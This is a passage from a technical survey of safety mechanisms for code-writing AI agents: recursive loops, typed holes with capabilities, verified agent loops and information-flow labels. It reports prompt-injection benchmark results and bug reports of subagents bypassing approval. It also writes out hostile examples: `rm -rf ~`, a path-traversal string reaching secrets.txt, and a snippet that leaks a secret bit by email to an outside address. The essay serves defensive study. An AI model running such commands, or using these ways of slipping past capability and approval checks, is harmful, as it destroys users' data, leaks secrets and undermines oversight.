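The recursive calls clearly help on OOLONG-Pairs. On CodeQA and BrowseComp+, OpenCode does about as well without them, so most of the gain there probably comes from keeping the input outside the prompt. Qwen3-Coder's BrowseComp+ score rose from 44.7 at recursion depth 1 to 68.7 at depth 3, but its OOLONG score fell from 48 to 32. Zhang and colleagues attribute the drop to syntax errors, which Qwen3-Coder makes often and repeats in its inner loops.

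The averages are misleading for someone approving a budget. The median run costs less than the median call to the model alone, but a few runs cost far more. Because costs can't be negative, a set of runs with mean cost μ and standard deviation σ must include at least one that cost about (μ² + σ²)/μ or more. For OOLONG at depth 2, that is more than $10, nearly ten times the average. Zhang and colleagues leave runaway costs from inner calls to future work.

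The number of calls depends heavily on the model. To find which of two labels was more common among 3,182 questions, Qwen3-Coder wrote a function that called an inner model once per question. GPT-5 makes around ten calls on simple tasks where Qwen3-Coder makes hundreds or thousands.

### Replications and the question of depth

In *Think, But Don't Overthink*, Wang (2026) ran the loop with two other open models, DeepSeek v3.2 and Kimi K2, before Zhang and colleagues published results beyond depth 1. On a simple search for a phrase hidden in a long text, DeepSeek scored 100% alone, 85% at depth 1 and 70% at depth 2, and the average time rose from 3.6 seconds to 344.5. In one failure, a depth-2 run that was supposed to find "magic numbers" in the text returned the magic numbers of nuclear physics (2, 8, 20, 28, 50, 82 and 126).

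On OOLONG, Kimi K2 fell from 86.6% alone to 60% at depth 1, while DeepSeek rose from 0% to 42.1%. DeepSeek's gain is overstated, because on its own it had found the answers but included explanations that the scoring rejected. Each figure comes from a single run of 20 questions, so only the large differences are informative.

Alizadeh, Shojaee and colleagues at Apple repeated the original experiments with GPT-5 and Qwen3-Coder, and concluded in *Recursive Language Models Meet Uncertainty* (2026) that recursion is not the main source of the gains. On CodeQA, GPT-5 scored 65.2 without inner calls and 59.5 with them, whereas Zhang and colleagues had found 58 and 62. The two papers also found opposite effects for Qwen3-Coder. CodeQA has only 50 questions, which is probably too few to settle the disagreement. Alizadeh and colleagues didn't test OOLONG-Pairs, where inner calls had helped GPT-5 a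 great deal.

A larger gain came from having the model attempt each job eight times and choosing among the attempts by agreement, stated confidence and length. With Qwen3-Coder, this raised the BrowseComp+ score from 37.1 to 59.7. It also means the model writes eight programs per job that reviewers haven't seen in advance, instead of one.

*Recursive Models for Long-Horizon Reasoning* (2026) shows that, in theory, recursion to a constant depth is no more powerful than simpler methods such as summarising, and that deeper recursion can solve more problems. But in practice, current models also pass their mistakes down to the inner loops.

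### What a reviewer can settle beforehand

A reviewer can approve the loop, the system prompt, the interpreter and the limits. These are the same whether the job is finding a pageant winner or reading a code repository, so approving them settles very little about how a particular job will go. How to divide the input, how many calls to make and what to ask in them are decided only during the run. In the audit-routes script, the reviewer could at least read the beginning and end of each agent's prompt.

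The system prompt recommends strategies but can't enforce them, so its advice doesn't guarantee any property of a run. Zhang and colleagues had to add a warning for Qwen3-Coder, which otherwise made thousands of inner calls for basic tasks. The warning suggests splitting 1,000 lines into groups of five, which still takes 200 calls. More detailed advice can help a lot. On LongCoT-mini, a set of long reasoning problems, GPT-5.2 solved 38.7% alone, 50.6% in the loop, and 65.6% in the loop when the prompt also explained how to split a problem into parts, solve them in order and check each answer.

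Limits in the code can cap the number of model calls in a run. *Using the RLM Client* gives a default limit of 30 rounds for the original RLM library, but a single round can contain a loop with any number of inner calls. DSPy, a framework for writing programs around language models, has a version that caps inner calls too. DSPy's *RLM* gives defaults of 20 rounds and 50 inner calls, plus one last call to try to produce an answer if the rounds run out. Excluding retries, a run therefore makes at most 71 model calls by default, though these limits don't restrict the length of each prompt.

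A tight cap on inner calls can rule out strategies that work. When Qwen3-Coder answered OOLONG questions correctly, it used about 500 inner calls on average. Under DSPy's default cap, it would have had to put many questions into each call.

Roy, Ji and colleagues (2026), in *The Y-Combinator for LLMs*, go further and fix the strategy itself. In their system, λ-RLM, a model only picks the kind of task from a menu. Ordinary code then splits the input, sends the pieces to a model and combines the replies. If the code splits each piece k ways until none is longer than τ tokens, an input of n tokens takes N = kᵈ + 1 model calls, where d is log_k(n/τ) rounded up and the extra call is the menu choice. For a million tokens, halved until no piece exceeds 100,000, d is 4 and the run makes 17 calls. (Dropping irrelevant pieces would lower the count, and asking a model to combine the replies would raise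 it.)

Across nine models and four tasks, λ-RLM beat the free-form loop in 29 of 36 comparisons and ran three to six times faster. But the free-form loop won 6 of the 12 comparisons with the strongest models. It did especially well on code repositories, where a model could split the code by function or go back over earlier files. All nine models are well behind today's best, so free-form code might now win more often.

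### A block that fails halfway

The loop runs each block as soon as the model has written it, without checking it first. As Zhao and colleagues point out, a faulty block can then fail partway and leave the interpreter in an inconsistent state. Suppose an earlier round has set `total` to 120, and the model sends these two lines:

```
total = total + count_matches(batch)
print("Total so far: " + total)
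```

The second line fails because Python won't join text to a number. By then the first line has added, say, 30 matches. If the model corrects the second line and sends both again, the code counts the batch twice, and the total becomes 180 instead of 150 with no error message. The model could have inspected `total` before trying again, but that check isn't automatic.

Python parses a whole block before running any of it, so a missing bracket stops the block before it changes anything. But a misspelt name or a value of the wrong type usually causes an error only when execution reaches it. Qwen3-Coder also tends to send several blocks in one reply, and an error in the third doesn't undo what the first two did. A compiler that checks types could reject both lines above before the addition runs.

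### When a sandbox is enough

One reply is that none of this matters much in a sandbox, an interpreter cut off from everything else. DSPy's default interpreter cannot access files or the network, and DSPy creates a new one for each run and discards it afterward. If the code miscounts, the user loses some money and gets a wrong answer, which an ordinary model call can also produce. The reply seems right for the tasks in these experiments, which only involve reading.

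Not every installation has such a sandbox. The RLM library runs generated code inside the host program by default, and *Recursive Language Models (RLMs)* advises against using this setting in production. *LocalREPL*, the documentation for the default interpreter, lists `eval` and `exec` as blocked, although the interpreter itself uses `exec` to run every piece of code. The interpreter also permits `open`, which can overwrite files, and doesn't isolate the code from the network. The library offers containers and cloud sandboxes as alternatives.

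The reply no longer holds once the generated code can call a tool with outside effects, and both packages let developers add such tools. If the first line of the faulty block had been `pay(customer, 40)`, the corrected block would pay the customer again, and discarding the interpreter wouldn't bring the money back. A prompt injection in the documents could also cause a payment.

Even without added tools, the inner calls reach outside the sandbox. Each one costs money and sends part of the input to whoever runs the inner model, which matters if the documents are confidential. Both packages can also keep an interpreter running between jobs, so a wrong total from one job could carry over into the next.

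If the interpreter is isolated and has no added tools, the whole loop takes in text and returns text, as a single model does, so a plan can use it wherever it would otherwise make one runtime model call. In the refund script, the loop could read ten years of a customer's correspondence and return a number, and the range check would still limit the payment to $50. The reviewer would have to confirm that the interpreter is isolated and that calls are capped, but wouldn't need to predict what code the model will write.

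## Generated code that is checked before it runs: LACUNA and ELBA

The loop in a recursive language model runs each block of Python as soon as a model has written it. In LACUNA, the system by Zhao and colleagues, the model writes in the language Scala, and the compiler checks how the parts of the program fit together before any of it runs. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a similar system for the language Haskell, called ELBA (TypeGuard in earlier versions). In both systems a model still writes code during the run, so a reviewer can't read that code in advance but can read the rules the compiler will apply to it.

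### Holes with a declared type

A *typed hole* is a place in a program where code is missing but the type of its result is already fixed. In `total = price + ___`, for example, the missing piece has to be a number. Earlier research treated holes as an aid to programmers. *Hazelnut* (Omar, 2016) describes an editor that puts holes where code is missing, so that an unfinished program still has a meaning after every edit. *Live Functional Programming with Typed Holes* (2018) defines what it means to run such a program. In *Statically Contextualizing Large Language Models with Typed Holes* (2024), Blinn, Li and colleagues had a language model fill the holes while the programmer was still writing and could read the code before running it.

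LACUNA fills in missing parts of a program while the program runs. The programmer writes `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is an instruction in English and `T` is the type of the result. When execution reaches this call, LACUNA sends a model the instruction, the expected type and the surrounding code. The model replies with a fragment of Scala. LACUNA puts the fragment in place of the call and compiles the combined text with the ordinary compiler, using the same settings as for the rest of the program. If compilation succeeds, LACUNA runs the fragment. Otherwise, it sends the compiler's error messages to the model, which tries again, up to a limit.

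JavaScript's `eval` gives a string the same access to the surrounding variables but doesn't check its types before running it. In the earlier `eval` example, a string could raise the payment limit with `limit = 100000`. A Scala programmer can declare `limit` as a constant with `val`, and the compiler then rejects any fragment that assigns it a new value. If the programmer declares it as a variable with `var`, the assignment is valid and the large payment goes through. A reviewer therefore has to check which keyword the scaffold uses.

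A type can describe a record or a function as well as a number or a piece of text. In one example from Zhao and colleagues, the program requests a `Person` with a name, a year of birth and a field of work. The model can't leave out the year or replace it with a word, but the compiler would accept a year that is wrong by a century. In another example, the program requests a function that turns numbers into Roman numerals. The model writes the function once, and the program can then use it repeatedly without calling a model again. A plan built this way could pause to show the function to a person before first using it.

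### A rejected fragment leaves the balance alone

Zhao and colleagues use a balance of 100 to show what happens when the compiler rejects a fragment. The balance is still 100 afterwards, because no part of the fragment has run. The fragment might look like this:

```
balance = balance - 30
log("New balance: " + blance)
```

The second line misspells the variable's name. Python would report the error only after running the first line, so running the corrected code could deduct the money twice. The Scala compiler reports it before either line runs, so the corrected code starts from 100 and leaves 70, as intended.

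The compiler accepts or rejects a fragment as a whole, but this doesn't protect against failures while an accepted fragment runs. If both lines are correct but the logging service is down, the second line fails after the deduction has already happened.

Many jobs also take more than one fragment. Generated code can end with another `agent` call to request the next one once the first fragment's results are known. The compiler therefore accepts the first fragment before the second exists. If the first cancels a flight and every attempt at the second fails to compile, the traveller has no replacement flight. ClauZ3 avoids this by checking both actions together, but the agent then has to write both before it cancels anything.

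### The names in scope as a set of permissions

Fixing the type of a result doesn't limit what the code does before returning it. A Scala fragment that returns a number could also send an email. LACUNA controls such effects with capabilities. A *capability* is a program value that code needs to perform a given effect, such as reading a file. Code can't create one itself and has to receive it from the surrounding program.

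The capabilities in scope at a hole, meaning those the code there can refer to by name, therefore act as the permissions of whatever code the model writes there. If the programmer makes a folder available at one hole and the network at another, code at the first can read files and code at the second can send data. An instruction hidden in a file may lead the model to write code at the first hole that sends the file's contents, but that code won't compile.

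Generated code also can't keep a capability for later. In an example from Zhao and colleagues, a block of the program has permission to read files. If the model's code has to return the contents of a file, it compiles, because the result is only text. If it has to return a function that reads files, the compiler rejects it, because the function would carry the permission out of the block. Scala can check this because a value's type can list the capabilities it holds, a feature called capture checking.

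Text can leave the block, though, and a later fragment with network access could send it. For confidential text, LACUNA borrows a wrapper from an earlier system called TACIT. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, explain that code can process the wrapped text only with functions that hold no capabilities, and the result stays wrapped. In their test of 131 attempts to make an agent reveal secrets, 2 succeeded against Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 11 against MiniMax M2.5 without the wrapper, and none succeeded against either model with it. In LACUNA, a function that processes wrapped text can also call a trusted model on the user's machine. That model can read the text and write code to suit it, but the code holds no capability for sending anything out.

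These checks depend on the compiler's settings. LACUNA's basic version uses only ordinary types, and the programmer has to switch on capture checking, which is still an experimental part of Scala. Generated code could also get around the checks by looking up functions by name while it runs or by starting another program. Scala has a safe mode that forbids both. Zhao and colleagues recommend using it, and advise treating generated code as ordinary untrusted code wherever safe mode is off.

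With the right settings, scope could restore the limit that the refund script lost when it began to run code from a model. The programmer could withhold `pay` and provide only a function called `refund`, which is already tied to the ticket, rejects any amount above $50 and works only once. The model could then write any amount of code to study the complaint, and the script still couldn't pay out more than $1,000. The reviewer would have to read `refund` and confirm that the generated code can't reach `pay`.

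### Three ways to write a code review

LACUNA lets a programmer choose how much of a function to leave to the model. Zhao and colleagues show this with a function that reviews a change to some code. In simplified form, its three versions are:

```
# Fully delegated
review(change) -> Review:
    agent[Review]("Apply the review checklist to this change.")

# Mixed
review(change) -> Review:
    risky = the files in change that are marked as risky
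    notes = for each file in risky:
                agent[Note]("Check this file against the list.")
    combine(notes)

# Fully written out
review(change) -> Review:
    notes = for each file in change: check(file)
    combine(notes)
```

In the first version, a reviewer knows only that the result will be a `Review`. The model might write code that looks at one file and ignores the rest. The second version guarantees a separate `agent` call for each risky file but ignores the other files. A reviewer can see this before the run and might object. In the third version, a model makes no decisions, assuming that `check` and `combine` are also ordinary code.

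All three versions have the same name, input and return type, so a program that calls `review` looks the same whichever version it uses. Somebody approving that program has to read the function to see how much it leaves open. In a long session, generated code can replace the function with a new one of the same name and type, and later `agent` calls will use the replacement. Zhao and colleagues suggest this as a way for agents to improve their own skills, but it also means that a fully delegated version could replace the written-out one that somebody approved.

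The type `Review` also doesn't stop the code from doing something else first. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) cites a bug report about Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in which a subagent assigned a read-only review generated an unrelated image and saved it outside the project. The programmer can prevent this by withholding the capability for writing files.

### ELBA and the trusted bibliography

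In Zhou and colleagues' main example, a user wants a bibliography on some topic. The agent may sort, filter and compare papers in any way, but every entry it writes must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. This rule is meant to keep out the citations that language models sometimes invent.

The programmer gives the agent three functions. The first searches DBLP and returns paper identifiers. The second fetches the full entry for an identifier and returns it with the type `Trusted Bib`. The third adds an entry to the bibliography file and accepts only a `Trusted Bib`. The code that creates `Trusted Bib` values is hidden inside the library, so a model that writes a convincing citation as text can't turn it into a value the third function accepts.

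The model could still write a program that skips the third function and writes to the file with Haskell's standard function. ELBA can catch this because Haskell is a pure language, meaning that the type of a piece of code shows which effects it may have. Standard file operations have the effect type `IO`. The programmer requires the agent's whole program to have a different effect type, `BibIO`, which only the three library functions can produce. A program that calls the standard function anywhere has the wrong type, and ELBA rejects it.

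The result type therefore restricts generated code more in ELBA than in LACUNA. If a Haskell program asks an agent for a plain whole number, the generated code can calculate but can't have outside effects. Zhou and colleagues describe a public calculator whose user asks the agent to delete all the files on the server and then calculate the factorial of 5. The model may well write that program, but the program won't pass the type check.

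They also tested the bibliography agent on 100 topics, using Claude Sonnet 5. None of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or DOI (the standard identifier for a publication). An ordinary agent with a web search tool got 19 of 1,002 wrong. But the type doesn't require the papers to be relevant. A program that adds nothing to the file would also pass, because an empty bibliography contains no invented entries.

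ELBA's agents can work in steps, as LACUNA's can. The generated program might run a search, read one result and then call a subagent to decide whether to search again or write to the file. The subagent's code runs inside a `BibIO` program, so it must have the type `BibIO` too. The parent can restrict the subagent further, for example by asking for a result that involves no effects, but it can't grant permissions that the parent itself lacks.

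Ordinary agent software doesn't always pass an agent's restrictions on to its subagents. In another bug report that Tan and colleagues cite, a session of the coding agent Goose required a person's approval for sensitive tools, but a subagent started in automatic mode and used them without approval.

### A guarantee for the whole program

Zhou and colleagues prove that any property a type guarantees still holds after a language gains an `agent` function, as long as each generated program passes the type check before it runs. A type t guarantees a property P if P(traces(e)) is true for every program e of type t, where traces(e) is the set of all sequences of tool calls with outside effects that e could make. For `BibIO`, P could be that every entry written to the file came from DBLP.

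The proof treats the model as a function that could return any program. It replaces every `agent` call with ordinary code that queries this function, checks the type of the answer and runs the answer if it passes. The new program has the same type and possible traces as the old one but contains no `agent` calls, so the original guarantee applies to it. Generated programs can contain further `agent` calls, so the proof assumes a limit on how deeply these calls nest and works up from depth zero.

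Such a P is a guaranteed property in the same sense as the refund script's $1,000 limit. A reviewer can verify it from the types before the run, no matter which model writes the code or what text that model has read.

The guarantee holds only if the whole system is written in the checked language, including the scaffold and the code that handles retries. If a Python script runs the bibliography agent and then has a model tidy up the formatting of the finished file, the model could add an invented entry that Haskell's compiler would never check. Most agent frameworks are written in Python, so few existing systems meet this condition.

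The library functions that assign the types also have to be correct. If the fetching function accepted entries from any website and labelled them `Trusted Bib`, every program would pass the check, even if its entries came from an untrusted site. A reviewer should probably spend most of their time on these functions, since every generated program depends on them.

### What LACUNA costs in completed tasks

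Zhao and colleagues tested LACUNA on the 830 research questions in BrowseComp-Plus with inexpensive models. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the generated fragments, and two thirds of the questions needed no second attempt. The agent answered 27.1% of the questions correctly. They say that the type check doesn't reduce accuracy, but they report no results for an unchecked agent on this benchmark.

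They do report one for τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations. The baseline agent uses the same models but calls its tools in the usual way instead of writing Scala. The table shows the share of tasks each agent solved.

| | DeepSeek, ordinary tool calls | DeepSeek, LACUNA | Gemini, ordinary tool calls | Gemini, LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9% | 58.8% | 52.6% | 43.9% |
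| Airline | 75.5% | 70.0% | 56.0% | 38.0% |
| Telecom | 100.0% | 88.6% | 15.8% | 14.9% |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4% | 83.3% | 21.1% | 24.6% |
| All 392 tasks | 90.0% | 76.0% | 33.2% | 29.1% |

The LACUNA paper's abstract describes the system as on par with the baseline. But with DeepSeek, LACUNA solved about 55 fewer tasks than the baseline, and its failure rate was 24%, compared with 10%. Each agent tried each task only once, but chance is very unlikely to explain a gap that large.

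Compiler errors may not be the main reason LACUNA scored lower than ordinary tool calls. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's fragments on the retail tasks, where the gap is widest. But it rejected only 3.2% of the fragments from Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite on the same tasks, and LACUNA still scored lower. On the telecom tasks, it rejected 89% of Gemini's fragments, and LACUNA scored almost the same as ordinary tool calls, though they scored so low that LACUNA's score had little room to fall.

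TACIT's results also suggest that writing typed Scala doesn't in itself lower scores. On the retail and airline tasks, three other models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls, averaged over ten runs. TACIT keeps the usual agent loop and checks only the code the agent submits. LACUNA also carries the conversation from one `agent` call to the next, and Zhao and colleagues concede that an ordinary loop may manage a long conversation better. A designer who mainly wants the type check could probably have it with a smaller drop in performance than LACUNA's scores suggest.

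Many rejected fragments contain ordinary programming mistakes, so the rejection rate doesn't measure how many accidents were prevented. The more relevant safety test used attacks from AgentDojo, the prompt-injection benchmark. Across two models, 8 of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA, compared with one each against TACIT and CaMeL. Zhao and colleagues point out that the type system doesn't block an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability the task needs.

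### ELBA when the attacker always wins the model over

Zhou and colleagues also used AgentDojo's tasks in a simulated Slack workspace. With ordinary attacks, all four models resisted every injection even without policies, so the results didn't show whether the policies worked. They therefore changed ELBA to simulate the worst case, in which any subagent that received data containing an attack followed the attacker's text instead of its own instructions. Seven runs of 105 attacks gave 735 trials for each model and setting.

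| Model | Injections resisted, no policies | Injections resisted, with policies | Tasks completed, no policies | Tasks completed, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

Without policies, up to 42% of the injections succeeded. With them, none did. (AgentDojo's own scoring flagged 29 of the 2,940 runs with policies. In each, the agent had opened a fixed web address, and Zhou and colleagues found no violation when they went through these runs by hand.)

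The policies also stopped a lot of legitimate work, cutting the number of tasks Opus 4.7 completed by about a third, from 523 to 351. Under the policies, an agent that reads untrusted data drops to the privileges of the data's source. This stops a malicious web page from directing a message to a colleague, but it can also stop a user from sending a colleague something from a harmless page. ELBA with policies still completed about twice as many of the Slack tasks as CaMeL did with its own policies, though it took about three times as long. One reason it completed more is that an ELBA subagent can read untrusted data and still use tools, which CaMeL's two-model design doesn't allow.

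A plan written before the model reads any data often lacks the step that an attacker needs, which can stop an attack even if other checks fail. ELBA gives up this protection for flexibility. *The LLMbda Calculus* notes that ELBA and TACIT let the model write new code after it has read hostile text, so their security depends entirely on the types and the libraries behind them.

In this test, much of the enforcement also happened during the run. The compiler made sure generated code could act only through a Haskell library called LIO, which labels data with its origin and stops the program when an action would break the policy. A reviewer can therefore rely on the forbidden message never going out, but can't tell in advance whether a given program will finish.

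### What a reviewer can approve without the code

For a plan with an ELBA or LACUNA hole, a reviewer can approve the expected type, the functions and capabilities in scope, the policies, and the libraries that enforce those policies. For the bibliography, that means three functions and one result type, which is much less to read than a 213-line NOVA plan. These are the same for every topic, so a reviewer who has read them carefully once doesn't have to reread them for the next bibliography.

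*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026), a paper by Amazon researchers, applies the same idea to tools that agents write for themselves. In the system it describes, an agent can turn a repeated task into a program in the language Lean. The program's type lists the permissions it needs, and the system admits the program only if the agent already has them. A person can read the list instead of the code. A human grants the first set of permissions, and an agent can't give a new subagent more than it has itself.

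Types can also cover the order of actions. In ETAS, the language by Tan and colleagues, a programmer can require that a program request approval before it changes a project, and the rule also applies to code in subagents. The compiler proves that the program follows the rule or, where it can't, adds a monitor that checks during the run. The rule requires a request only before the first change, so one request is enough for any number of changes. The program needs an ordinary `if` statement to check that the person said yes.

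Richer types could allow more of the review to happen earlier. Zhao and colleagues propose types that restrict values, for example to whole numbers within a range. The refund script could then require code that provably returns a value between 0 and 50. Zhou and colleagues mention types for single-use permissions, which would rule out a second payment.

No such type can express that a customer really bought a broken kettle. Generated code can stay within its permissions and still choose the wrong method, call the wrong function or return a plausible but false answer. LACUNA requests a new fragment only if the old one doesn't compile, so a fragment that compiles runs even if it does the wrong thing. Whether well-typed code does the right thing remains a deferred decision, which somebody has to make by judging the code or its results.

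The problem also arises without an attack. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) cites measurements in which Claude Code took actions nobody had asked for at rates from 0.0% to 17.1%, depending only on the wording of the prompt. Capabilities don't stop such an action if the agent already holds the one it needs for another part of the job. The survey notes that the access-control research it covers takes the policy as given. It found no work on what happens when a policy's author grants too much, perhaps to save the time of writing a narrower policy. ELBA's losses on legitimate tasks give programmers another reason to loosen a policy.

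### Code that never finishes

Types in these systems also don't limit how long code runs or how much it costs. A fragment can contain an endless loop, and an agent can keep calling itself. As Zhao and colleagues note, the type system can't distinguish a runaway recursion from a hard problem that needs many steps. They set limits outside the type system, such as ten minutes for each BrowseComp-Plus question and at most 128 nested calls. On τ²-bench, a task could use at most 500 tool calls. People have to choose these limits, and one set too low will stop a task that only needed more time or calls.

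L3M treats money somewhat like a permission. A parent lends part of its budget to its subagents, and Eisenach and colleagues prove that the whole group can't spend more than the parent had. The proof covers a single round of lending, and they say later loans and repayments need further work.

A weak model can also get stuck without doing any harm. The 89% of Gemini's telecom fragments that failed to compile changed nothing, but each one used a model call without helping to solve the customer's problem. Better models reduce this waste. ELBA's agents, which ran on much stronger models, averaged 0.13 retries per run, though in a different language and on different tasks.

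Odersky and colleagues note that code with access to a wrapped secret could take longer to run for one value than for another, and so reveal a bit of the secret to anyone who can time it. Their type system doesn't cover this.

A reviewer therefore needs to look in the scaffold for the limits on time, calls and spending, because the types don't set them. The reviewer should also check what happens when the plan reaches a limit, because a refund script that stops after paying a customer but before closing the ticket may pay again on the next run.

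## Proofs that hold whatever the model answers: PocketFlow and the LLMbda calculus

In ELBA, the compiler has to check each program after a model has written it. The fixed part of a plan can also be proved to have certain properties before any model has answered, provided the proof allows for every answer a model could give. Two projects from 2026 do this for whole agent systems. One project's proof covers the loop that carries out an agent's actions, and the other's covers every program in a small language called LLMbda, including programs that models write during the run.

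### The refund limit as a proof

People who verify software often have to reason about a value they can't predict, such as a user's input. They can replace it with an arbitrary value and require the proof to work for all of them. *Havoc semantics* is a way of verifying a program that lets a call return any value of its declared type. Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, writes the arbitrary value as an asterisk. In roughly that notation, the refund script becomes:

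```
paid, n := 0, 0
while n < 20
    invariant n <= 20 and paid <= 50 * n
{
    answer := *                      // any whole number at all
    if 0 <= answer <= 50 { paid := paid + answer }
    n := n + 1
}
assert paid <= 1000
```

Here `n` counts the tickets and `paid` counts the dollars. The invariant must be true before the loop starts and after every pass. At the start both counts are 0, so it holds. Suppose it holds before some pass, so paid ≤ 50n. If the answer is between 0 and 50, the script pays it, and the new total is at most 50n + 50 = 50(n + 1). Otherwise the total doesn't change, so it is still below 50(n + 1). The loop ends when n is 20, and then paid ≤ 50 × 20 = 1,000. The verifier doesn't have to check each of the 51²⁰ possible lists of answers.

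Finding the right invariant takes some thought. The verifier would reject the simpler statement `paid <= 1000` as an invariant, even though it is true throughout every run. The verifier checks one pass at a time, and that statement alone doesn't rule out a pass that starts with $980 already paid and pays another $50.

An asterisk can also stand for a yes/no answer. The verifier would then have to assume that the water-filter plan could place an order at any price.

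Havoc semantics applies the every-run reading to the model's answers, so the proof must cover every answer the model could give. Because the proof assumes nothing about the model, it still holds if someone swaps in a worse model or an attacker takes control of the current one. Dantas and colleagues describe the same treatment in model checking, where software explores a graph of the agent's possible states and the language model may take any available step.

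However, the proof depends on the declared type of `ask_model` being correct. Suppose the author declares that it returns a whole number from 0 to 50 and then deletes the range check as unnecessary. The proof still succeeds, because the verifier assumes that outside code returns its declared type. But nothing tests the actual answer during the run, so if the model returns 400, the script pays $400. The Dafny manual describes this problem and recommends declaring a wider type and testing the value in the program.

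### A verified loop for agents

*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) applies havoc semantics to a general framework, PocketFlow, instead of a single script. PocketFlow is deliberately small and represents an agent as a graph of steps. After each step, the framework follows the edge whose label matches the action the step produced. In the Dafny version of this loop, the model is a method with no body, which may return any value of type `Action`.

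The policy lets the agent read only files in its workspace folder, call only tools on a list, and take no more than a set number of steps. The loop rejects any other request from the model, so the request has no outside effect.

The proof compares two descriptions of the system. M is an abstract model of what the loop should do, and I is a detailed model of how it works. In both, an action a in state s produces a boundary event e, such as reading a file, and a new state s′. A policy Π(s, a, e, s′) is a test that each step passes or fails. The theorem is then:

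```
if     Π_M(s, a, e, s′) holds at every step of every run of M
and    I refines M
then   Π_I(s, a, e, s′) holds at every step of every run of I
```

The first assumption covers every sequence of actions an AI could choose. The second, refinement, means that the two models start in matching states, that every step of I has a matching step of M with the same action, and that whenever the step of M passes its policy, the matching step of I passes too. The proof takes any run of I, builds the matching run of M one step at a time, and concludes that the steps of I pass because the matching steps of M do. Dafny checked the theorem and, for PocketFlow, both assumptions.

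These results concern a model of the loop. They extend to a deployed agent only if every outside effect passes through the modelled interface, a condition Moon and Varshney call effect exclusivity. If one step of the agent contains a line of Python that uploads a file directly, the loop never receives an action to check and the theorem doesn't apply. They therefore recommend running the verified loop inside a sandbox.

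The three rules are also weaker than they may sound. If Michelle's agent has both `fetch_mail` and `send_email` on its list, it can send her summary to a stranger without breaking any of them, because they check which tool is called, not what it sends. The theorem would allow a stricter policy, since Π can also depend on an action's arguments. For the file rule, the published lemma requires each path to start with the workspace folder's name. If the check only compares text, `/workspace/../secrets.txt` passes, even though the two dots lead out of the folder.

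A rule can also be true only because nothing it restricts ever occurs. Moon and Varshney had Claude models write the formal specifications, starting from a template that records files read and tools called. One of their two test agents did neither and only read documents from an approved list. When the model writing the specification could see the agent's code, it identified that the template had no place for documents and left the list of tool calls empty at every step. The rule "Every tool call is on the approved list" was then true because no tool calls were recorded. Dafny accepted the proof, and so did three extra checks meant to catch bad specifications. When the model could not see the code, it recorded the documents as tool calls, so the rule applied to them. A reviewer of such a proof should check whether the actions it restricts ever occur in the formal model.

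### When one permitted action is a shell command

PocketFlow's guarantee depends on a narrow interface with only four kinds of action. Suppose a developer adds a fifth, `RunShell(command)`. Under havoc semantics the command can be any text, so the proof has to hold for `ls`, which lists files, for `rm -rf ~`, which deletes the user's files, and for a command that downloads a program and runs it.

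A proof that every command passes through the loop would be easy, but a reviewer would learn almost nothing from it. A useful policy might forbid commands from deleting anything outside the workspace. To enforce it, the loop would have to predict each command's effects from its text alone.

In *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified*, Franco and Gershenson (2026) use standard results about computability to show that no program can do this exactly. Given one dangerous program, no filter can block every program that behaves the same way and nothing else. A finite list of forbidden programs always misses some, because there are infinitely many ways to write a program with the same behavior. Permitting only named tools doesn't help if one of them is an interpreter such as `python3`, because the agent can pass it a file that contains the dangerous program.

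Limits on time and memory make the question answerable in principle, but answering it takes a lot of computation. Franco and Gershenson show that a checker that can only run the agent and watch must, for some agents, visit every possible state of the agent's memory. A memory with ten entries that can each take ten values has more than ten billion states.

Their title promises more than this, and I think a reviewer can be less gloomy than it suggests.

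The results rule out a checker that gives the right verdict on every agent, but still allow one that refuses any plan it can't prove safe. The only drawback of such a checker is that it rejects some harmless plans. The refund script passes because its author wrote it to be easy to prove safe.

A loop that permits only the shell commands it can prove safe ends up with a short list of exact commands, such as `ls` and `git status`. This gives a real guarantee, but the agent loses general use of the shell. Moon and Varshney accept this point, and write that a general shell or `eval` action reduces their guarantee to whatever that action itself guarantees. With such an action, any useful limit has to come from the sandbox.

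Verified programs can also fail because the formal rules left something out. In *MAGS* (2026), language models turned safety requirements into formal rules and wrote programs to satisfy them. Dafny verified all 100 terminal programs, but only 82 passed an independent security test. The 100 programs for graphics chips and 20 robot policies passed both verification and their independent tests, because the formal rules in those areas already included what the tests measured.

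### Labels that follow the data

PocketFlow proves limits on which actions an agent can take. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) instead tracks where the data in each action came from. Its language, LLMbda, is the source of the earlier example in which a program fixes an email's subject and body while a model extracts the recipient's address from an incoming message.

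An LLMbda program maintains a conversation with a model. The operator `@` sends a prompt and runs the reply as code, though the reply may be just a number or text. `fork` does some work on a copy of the conversation and then discards the copy, and `clear` empties the conversation. A programmer can build the two-model design used for computer-use plans by having the program fork the conversation, clear the copy and send the prompt there, so the untrusted text never enters the main conversation.

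Every value carries a label. In the simplest version, the label marks the value as untrusted, secret, both or neither, and results inherit the labels of their inputs, as in Meijer's checker. In the email example, the incoming message is untrusted, and so is the address that a model extracts from it. The subject and body are neither untrusted nor secret, because the planning model wrote them before anyone read the message. The `send_email` tool requires a trusted subject and body but accepts an untrusted address. If a program breaks this rule, the interpreter stops it.

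Labels are easy to get wrong, because a program can reveal a secret without copying it. Garby and colleagues found such a gap in CaMeL, the earlier two-model system for email and calendar tools. Simplified, it looks like this:

```
rich = True
test = True
if balance > threshold: test = False
if test:                rich = False
if rich:                send_email(to="someone@outside.example", body="rich")
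```

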